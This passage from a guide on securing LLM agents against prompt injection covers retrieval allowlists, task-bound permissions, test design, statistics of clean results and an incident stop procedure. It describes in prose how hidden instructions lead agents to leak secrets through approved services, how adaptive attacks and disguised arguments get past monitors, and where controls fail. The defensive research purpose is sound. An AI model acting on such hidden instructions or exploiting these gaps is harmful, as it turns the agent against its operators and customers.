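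Alhindi then replaced the email-reading agent with ordinary software that extracts the invoice number, order number, total and supplier. In another 40 runs, the note never reached an agent and no account changed. A list of approved senders would have let this email through, because the address was genuine. Extracting fields gives better protection, but only for tasks that need a few predictable values, so it wouldn't work for an agent that has to answer a customer's complaint.

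*Prismata* (Villa and Tan, 2026) comes closest to combining the two controls. The system labels the parts of a web page by how far the agent should trust them, then hides content and restricts actions accordingly. Villa and Tan report that attacks, including adaptive ones, succeeded substantially less often. But the system judges trust within each page instead of using a fixed list of sources, so the result can't be applied to a retrieval allowlist.

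### Both controls in one calculation

A rough calculation can still show how the two controls might work together. It uses the expected-harm model and the formula for repeated attempts, with these assumptions:

- The model obeys 1% of the hostile instructions it reads (an invented figure).
- The retrieval allowlist keeps out 80% of hostile items (also invented).
- One obeyed instruction gives the attacker full control of the agent for that session. The average harm is then 10.00 without permission limits and 0.69 with task-bound permissions, as in the Aljumaily simulation.
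- Each attempt is independent of the others, and each control works equally well with or without the other.

If r is the share of hostile items that reach the model, p is the chance that it obeys and H is the average harm from a compromised agent, the expected harm after k attempts is:

harm(k) = (1 − (1 − r × p)^k) × H

This counts the harm from one successful attack, even if several succeed. The last column assumes the attacker has taken over an approved source, so the allowlist blocks nothing.

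| Controls | 1 attempt | 1,000 attempts | 1,000 attempts from an approved source |
|---|---|---|---|
| Neither | 0.1000 | 10.0 | 10.0 |
| Retrieval allowlist | 0.0200 | 8.6 | 10.0 |
| Task-bound permissions | 0.0069 | 0.69 | 0.69 |
| Both | 0.0014 | 0.60 | 0.69 |
| Both, with a fifth of the permission rules missing | 0.0032 | 1.4 | 1.6 |

Against a single attempt, the allowlist reduces expected harm fivefold, task-bound permissions reduce it about 14-fold, and the two together about 72-fold. Against 1,000 attempts, the allowlist alone reduces expected harm by only 14%, because about 200 hostile items still reach the model and the attacker needs only one to succeed. Task-bound permissions still reduce it 14-fold, because they limit what the attacker gains from that success.

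The allowlist would need to block about 99% of hostile items to keep the chance of a compromise below 10% over 1,000 attempts. A strict document manifest might do this, but a list of web domains that includes forums probably wouldn't. A more resistant model also makes the allowlist more useful. If the model followed only 0.1% of hostile instructions, the allowlist alone would lower the expected harm from 1,000 attempts from 6.3 to 1.8.

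The weakest assumption is that the controls work independently. An attacker who gets past the allowlist has often taken over a trusted source, such as a supplier's mailbox, and a supplier can plausibly ask for a payment or a change of bank details. Attacks that get past the first control may therefore be unusually likely to get past the second, in which case the true reduction would be less than 72-fold. Yingyan He found in the LightRAG tests that the layers of a defence affected one another so strongly that nobody could isolate what each contributed.

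*Where Agent Defenses Fail* (2026) describes an attack that gets past two controls on an agent's actions, a rule on destinations and a sandbox with no network connection of its own. The agent's task is to upload a status report to an approved service, but a hidden instruction tells it to upload a file of secrets to the same service. The destination rule permits the request, and a program outside the sandbox that delivers approved requests sends the secrets. A retrieval allowlist would also let the hidden instruction through if it came from an approved source. Before multiplying the effects of several controls to estimate their combined effect, an operator should look for a route like this one, which all of them have to leave open for the agent to do its job.

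## Testing the controls before and after deployment

A well-designed permission rule can still fail because someone misspelled a domain or left one tool outside the monitor. Testing finds such mistakes, and the tests that take the least effort should come first. Suppose the online shop is about to deploy its support agent. The agent has the reduced permissions from the worked inventory. It answers questions using a library of product manuals and returns policies, and a manifest limits what it can read there.

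### Forbidden calls sent without the model

The shop first sends tool calls straight to the policy monitor and the sandbox, as if an attacker already controlled the agent. Fokou calls this assume-compromise evaluation in *PARALLAX* (April 2026).

The test leaves out the model because a well-trained model can hide faults in the controls. In Fokou's preliminary runs, Claude Sonnet 4.6, Claude Haiku 4.5 and Llama 3.1 8B refused every harmful request, with or without outside controls, so a broken monitor would have received the same perfect score as a working one.

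Fokou therefore wrote a program that sends calls directly to Shield, the part of the Parallax system that checks each call before it runs. Shield applies fixed rules, then a pattern matcher and a trained classifier, then a second language model, and in a few cases asks a person for approval. The test had 280 harmful calls in nine categories and 57 legitimate ones, seven of which tested only that approval step.

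| Configuration | Harmful calls blocked | Legitimate calls wrongly blocked |
|---|---|---|
| Shield off | 0 of 280 | – |
| Default | 277 of 280 | 0 of 50 |
| Strictest | 280 of 280 | 18 of 50 |

In the default configuration, seven kinds of action, including writing files and sending email, skip the classifier because it often wrongly flags them as attacks. One of the three harmful calls that got through was a command that lists environment variables, including any keys stored there. The second model had labeled it a harmless read operation.

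With Shield off, the attack success rate is 100% by construction, because there is no model to refuse a call and no monitor to block it. In a benchmark such as AgentDojo, some attacks fail because the model ignores them, so Progent's results on AgentDojo can't be compared with Parallax's reduction from 100% to 1.1%. The useful results of a direct test are the list of malicious calls that got through and the number of legitimate calls that were blocked.

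Fokou's 98.9% is also a favorable figure, because the first version of the rules did worse. Testing showed that that version didn't cover credential files, system files or the agent's own folders. Fokou added rules for these and 17 new patterns for shell attacks, and reported the results of the improved version. The final score therefore partly measures how well the rules stop the attacks used to improve them.

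An operator can avoid this by setting some attacks aside until the rules are finished. *SPILLWAY* (2026), which tests a defense for tool-using agents, did this after adding payment rules. It used two sets of 144 banking cases that nobody had used to write the rules. One attack succeeded in the first set (two under a stricter count) and none in the second. However, the attacks had been tuned against other systems.

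For the shop, the most informative calls are those just outside a permission, each paired with a similar call that should work.

| Should work | Should fail |
|---|---|
| Refunding $50 on the ticket's order | Refunding $51, refunding $50 on another order, or refunding $50 twice |
| Replying to the ticket's sender | The same reply with a second recipient |
| Reading the record of the ticket's customer | Reading another customer's record, or changing this one |
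| Opening a manual on the manifest | Opening a copy of the manual with one digit changed |

The shop should also test disguised versions of the forbidden arguments. Aljumaily and colleagues wrote numbers as text, changed the capitalization of argument names and attached forbidden shell commands to permitted ones. To score the test, the shop should check whether money moved or a message was sent, because a log entry that reads "denied" doesn't prove that nothing happened. Dehghantanha recommends comparing files before and after each test, inspecting network records and never letting the tested system grade itself.

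Some direct tests can run every time the agent starts. Before Fokou's agent accepts any request, it tries to write a file on the host computer, read a known file there, connect to an unauthorized address and reach the process that enforces the rules. If any attempt succeeds, the agent won't start. This would catch a sandbox that had silently failed to load.

### Hidden instructions against the whole agent

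Next, the shop plants hidden instructions in test tickets and runs the complete agent on them. This measures how often the model follows them and how much harm the agent can do with its permitted calls. It also tests any control that relies on a model, such as one that writes permissions for each request.

The shop needs to test with adaptive attacks as well as fixed ones. *AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) uses a language model to write new hidden instructions based on which earlier ones worked, inferring the kind of defense it faces. The only feedback it gets is whether each attempt succeeded. PIGuard, a classifier that detects injections, stopped every fixed attack on an agent running GPT-4o mini, but 28% of the adaptive ones succeeded. Five of the ten defenses kept the success rate of fixed attacks close to zero on this agent, but only one of those five, Progent, also withstood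 the adaptive attacks.

*Defending against Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks via Reasoning-enabled Task Alignment* (2026) found that adaptive attacks succeeded up to 50% of the time against defenses that had done well on fixed attacks. The gap is probably exaggerated, because the fixed attacks were tested on 420 cases and the adaptive attacks on only 40 cases already known to be vulnerable.

Ma and colleagues also found that attacks succeeded far more often when the user left the choice of action to the content, as in "do what this email asks". The shop should therefore word its test requests as vaguely as its staff word their real ones.

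An adaptive attack can also be too weak to test a defense well. Narisetty, Kore and colleagues (2026), in *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents*, tested Progent with a small open model. Fixed attacks succeeded 25.8% of the time without Progent and 4.2% with it. Their adaptive attack, which presented the harmful action as a routine step the user had already approved, succeeded only 2.6% of the time. They suspect the gentler wording made the agent itself less likely to obey. They didn't test the attacker the shop should worry about most, one who uses only permitted actions.

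Every attack should first succeed with the controls off. In the same experiment, no attack on the office tasks succeeded even without Progent, because the model read the hidden instructions and ignored them, so those tasks did not test Progent. *Injection-Execution Dissociation* (2026), a study of attacks through an agent's memory, first reported that a sandbox made attacks more successful, but its comparison without a sandbox was faulty. In the corrected comparison, every attack succeeded without the sandbox, and the sandbox lowered the success rate in all four conditions tested. If a current model ignores every attack the shop can devise, the shop can use a model that is more likely to follow hidden instructions for this test, or rely on the direct calls.

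The shop also has to confirm that the hidden text reached the model. *AgentS4D* (Zhou, Ke and colleagues, 2026) ran 328 attack cases on 20 combinations of model and agent software and checked the records for this. Agents did something unsafe in 68% of all runs. That figure rose to 76% after excluding inconclusive runs and runs where the agent acted safely but nobody could confirm that it had met the attack. Covertly embedded instructions succeeded 99% of the time in add-on bundles of instructions and scripts, but 47% of the time in connected tool services. A shop that tests only emails may therefore miss a weakness in how the agent reads attachments.

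In 66% of all runs, the agent did something unsafe and still completed the user's task, so a finished task is no evidence that an attack failed. Automatic scoring can also miss attacks. Two of the researchers on the Aljumaily simulation checked samples of its real-model runs by hand and found that the scoring program undercounted attacks the model had carried out in different words. Dehghantanha suggests having people check 10 to 20% of the results.

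### Ordinary tasks and wrongly blocked actions

The shop then runs real, harmless tickets with the controls on to check that ordinary work still gets done. One guard in *CT0* (2026) reduced successful attacks from 16 to 4 out of 64, but completed ordinary tasks also fell from 23 to 13 out of 32.

The ordinary tasks should be separate from the attack tests and as varied as the agent's real work. In *LivePI* (2026), a set of seven custom rules stopped all the attacks. The paper also ran the protected agent on a second benchmark of writing, coding, email and research tasks, and reported little loss in performance.

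The comparison is more precise if the shop runs the same tickets with and without the controls. It learns little about the controls from tickets that succeed both times or fail both times, so it can concentrate on those where the outcome changed. The shop should also log every blocked call and have someone decide whether the block was correct.

Completion alone can hide the work that the controls create for people. Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, therefore measure the share of tasks that an agent completes with at most k human approvals:

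TCR@k = (tasks completed with k or fewer approvals) / (all tasks)

If the shop's agent has a task completion rate (TCR) of 80% at TCR@0 and 97% at TCR@1, it handles 80% of tickets alone and needs one approval for another 17%. Kolluri and colleagues point out that earlier studies compared protected agents that couldn't ask for approval with unprotected agents that effectively had unlimited approvals. In practice, many unprotected agents ask for approval before every consequential action. On AgentDojo, a basic system that tracks where data came from reduced approvals by a factor of up to 1.5 compared with such an agent, with no loss in completed tasks.

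### Marked documents outside the allowlist

To test the retrieval allowlist, the shop plants harmless documents that the agent should never receive. Each contains a marker, a string that occurs nowhere else. *ContextLeak* (2025) uses 64 random hexadecimal digits, and *Behavioral Canaries* (2026) adds markers to otherwise realistic documents and asks questions that match them. Both were designed for other kinds of privacy audit, but the same method works here:

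1. Write several realistic documents, such as a returns policy for a product that doesn't exist. Give each its own marker and a distinctive false fact, such as a returns period of 43 days.
2. Put one in each place that the allowlist should exclude. These could include an unregistered file in the library folder, an altered copy of an approved manual, a page on an unlisted site and a page behind a redirect from a listed site.
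3. Register one more marked document on the manifest as a comparison.
4. Ask questions for which each document would be the best match, using every tool that can retrieve text.
5. Search everything the model received for the markers and the false facts.

Searching only the agent's answers isn't enough, because the model can read a document without repeating it. The test needs the false facts because indexing software may rewrite a document and drop the random string, as LightRAG could when it merges descriptions. If the registered document doesn't appear either, the search is broken and the test is invalid.

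The test should use every tool because two tools may reach the same content. In *Injection-Execution Dissociation*, a defense covered the tool that recalled memories, but GPT-5.1 could get the same text through document search. The shop should run the test on a copy of the library so that no customer receives the false returns policy.

### How much a clean result proves

If a control fails at a true rate p, the chance of seeing no failure in n independent trials is (1 − p)ⁿ. The highest rate that is still compatible with a clean result at 95% confidence is the one that makes this chance 5%:

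p = 1 − 0.05^(1/n) ≈ 3/n

| Independent trials without a failure | True failure rate could still be |
|---|---|
| 50 | 5.8% |
| 156 | 1.9% |
| 299 | 1.0% |
| 1,000 | 0.3% |
| 2,995 | 0.1% |

The same limits apply to wrongly blocked actions. Parallax blocked none of 50 legitimate calls in its default configuration, but the true rate could be almost 6%. At that rate, a task with 20 calls would have a 70% chance of at least one wrong block, assuming the blocks are independent.

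A few strong attacks can provide more evidence than many weak ones. *What AI Red-Team Evaluations Can and Cannot Prove* (Kaur, 2026) compares how likely a clean result is for a safe system and for an unsafe one. Suppose an attack would succeed 90% of the time against a bad control and 10% of the time against a good one. One failed attempt then multiplies the odds that the control is good by nine. If the attacks succeed 0.1% of the time against a bad control and 0.05% against a good one, it would take about 4,400 failed attempts to get the same evidence.

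Repeating a few tasks proves less than the table suggests, because attempts at the same task tend to have the same outcome. The larger model in the Aljumaily tests, with spotlighting and a detector, carried out none of 156 attacks, but these came from only 13 tasks. A common correction estimates how many independent trials the attempts are worth:

effective trials = n / (1 + (m − 1) × ρ)

Here m is the number of attempts per task and ρ is the correlation between attempts at the same task. *ClawsBench* (2026), a benchmark of office agents, measured a correlation of 0.48 in a pilot. With that value and 12 attempts per task, 156 attempts are worth about 25 independent ones, and the true rate could be as high as 11%. If every attempt at a task had the same outcome, the 13 tasks would count as 13 trials, and the true rate could be as high as 21%. The correlation in the Aljumaily tests may differ,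 but it seems to have been high, because all 12 attacks that succeeded against the same model behind the task-bound monitor came from one task. The likely range for that monitor was 4 to 13% when the attempts were treated as independent, and 0 to 23% after allowing for the choice of tasks.

Consistent results across repeated runs can be misleading for the same reason. Narisetty and colleagues ran their whole study three times and got nearly identical averages, but each run used the same eight user tasks per suite. In the extreme case, a fixed rule always returns the same result for the same call, so trying one forbidden refund a thousand times shows no more than trying it once. The shop should test a thousand different calls instead.

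A reported attack success rate of 0% is meaningful only if the report also states the number of tasks, the number of attempts at each, and how the testers chose them. *Limits of Statistical Assurance for Embodied and Agentic AI under Adaptive Adversaries* (2026) found that AI developers' reports differ on these points. Some count repeated runs of a single task, while others count tasks with up to 30 attempts each. Even a well-designed test supports conclusions only about attacks similar to those it included.

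### Signs of failure in use

Controls that pass every test can weaken later as people add exceptions and the agent's work changes.

| Sign | What to record | Likely cause |
|---|---|---|
| Growing exceptions | New tools, recipients, folders or domains permitted each week | The rules don't fit the work, or an attacker is widening them |
| Unused permissions | The date when the agent last used each permission | The task has changed, or nobody needed the permission |
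| Expired domains | The registration date and owner of each listed domain | Nobody is maintaining the list |
| Repeated denied calls | Denials by tool, argument and source of the request | A missing permission, a confused agent or an attack |
| Controls switched off | The share of sessions without the monitor or sandbox | Too many wrongly blocked actions |

For agents whose permissions change with each request, *LLM Agent Authorization Across Context Compaction* (2026) defines a policy as expanded if it permits a tool that changes something, or an argument value, that the previous policy didn't. Software can count these expansions, and a person can check whether the user asked for them.

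Denied calls are harder to interpret. Kolluri and colleagues found that in most failed runs without an attack, the agent kept trying calls that the policy didn't allow. The shop should look at what a denied call would have achieved before treating it as an attack. Twenty denied refunds on the right order suggest that the limit is too low, but the shop should immediately investigate even one attempt to email a stranger. A sudden drop to no denials is also suspicious, because the monitor may have stopped running.

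Fokou compares users who disable strict controls with those who turned off overzealous antivirus software. Once many sessions run without the controls, a clean record from the remaining sessions is weak evidence of the shop's overall risk. It is usually better to fix the rule that causes the most wrong blocks and let only an administrator switch the controls off.

### A review schedule

The testing intervals below are reasonable starting points. Organizations that change their agent every day, or whose agent can move large sums of money, need shorter ones.

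| When | What to check |
|---|---|
| At every start | Sandbox probes |
| After any change to the model, instructions, tools or rules | Direct calls, ordinary tasks and marked documents |
| Weekly | Denied calls, new exceptions and sessions without controls |
| Monthly | Unused permissions, and the owner and expiry date of every listed domain |
| Every three months, and after a major model change | Adaptive attacks and a stop drill |

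Dehghantanha suggests blocking any update that raises the rate of unsafe actions by more than two percentage points for any type of attack. That threshold is too fine for a small test. With 100 independent trials per run and a true rate of 5%, an unchanged agent's second run will show a rate more than two points higher than its first about a fifth of the time. For fixed rules, the shop can use a stricter and more reliable standard by blocking any update that allows a forbidden call to succeed where it used to fail.

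### The stop procedure

When the shop suspects that an attacker controls the agent, it should stop the agent before investigating. One named person on each shift needs the authority and the access to do this without asking anyone.

1. Revoke the agent's tokens at the services that accept them. Deleting a token from the sandbox leaves any stolen copy working.
2. Cut the agent's network access at the proxy outside the sandbox. This also covers tokens that stay valid for a few minutes after someone revokes them.
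3. Pause the sandbox, and cancel queued messages, scheduled jobs and tasks handed to other agents.
4. Copy the logs, the sandbox's files and the text the model received to storage that the agent can't change. Only then delete the sandbox.
5. List what the agent read, changed and sent since the attack began. Restore changed files from backups and warn anyone who received a false message.
6. Add the attack to the direct tests, and restart the agent with new tokens once the test fails to reproduce it.

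The logs are better evidence if each entry contains a fingerprint of the previous one, as in Fokou's system, because an entry that is changed later will no longer match its fingerprint. The system also saves a copy of each file before changing or deleting it, which makes step five easier.

The shop should practice the procedure with a harmless incident, such as an agent stuck in a loop, and time it. Dehghantanha defines "time to contain" as the interval from the start of an incident to its containment, and recommends reporting the slowest drills as well as the median. An agent that makes a call every five seconds will make 120 more calls if the staff need ten minutes to stop it.

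### Acceptance checklist

| Requirement | Evidence that satisfies it |
|---|---|
| The shop knows what the agent can reach | A dated inventory of credentials, tools, files and network routes, with a traced worst case for each |
| The monitor blocks forbidden calls | Results for calls just outside every permission, including disguised arguments and calls kept back while writing the rules, with service records that show no effect |
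| The sandbox is running | Failed start-up probes, and a record that the agent refused to start when a tester disabled the sandbox |
| The sandbox contains no reusable secrets | A search of its files and environment variables that finds no working key |
| The network rules hold | Failed connections to unlisted addresses, and an owner, reason and expiry date for every listed domain |
| The attack tests are valid | Records that each attack reached the model and worked with the controls off |
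| Attacks rarely succeed | Successes, distinct tasks and attempts per task, with an upper limit that allows for repeated tasks; results for adaptive attackers and for attackers who use only permitted actions |
| Ordinary work continues | Completion of the same tasks with and without the controls, approvals per task and a reviewed list of wrong blocks |
| The retrieval allowlist holds | Complete model inputs that contain the approved marker and none of the others |
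| Exceptions stay under control | A log that gives each exception an owner, a reason and an end date |
| Staff can stop the agent | A timed drill in which the revoked token failed, the connection closed and the logs survived |
| Someone accepts the remaining risk | A signed description of the worst action the agent can still take, with its estimated cost |
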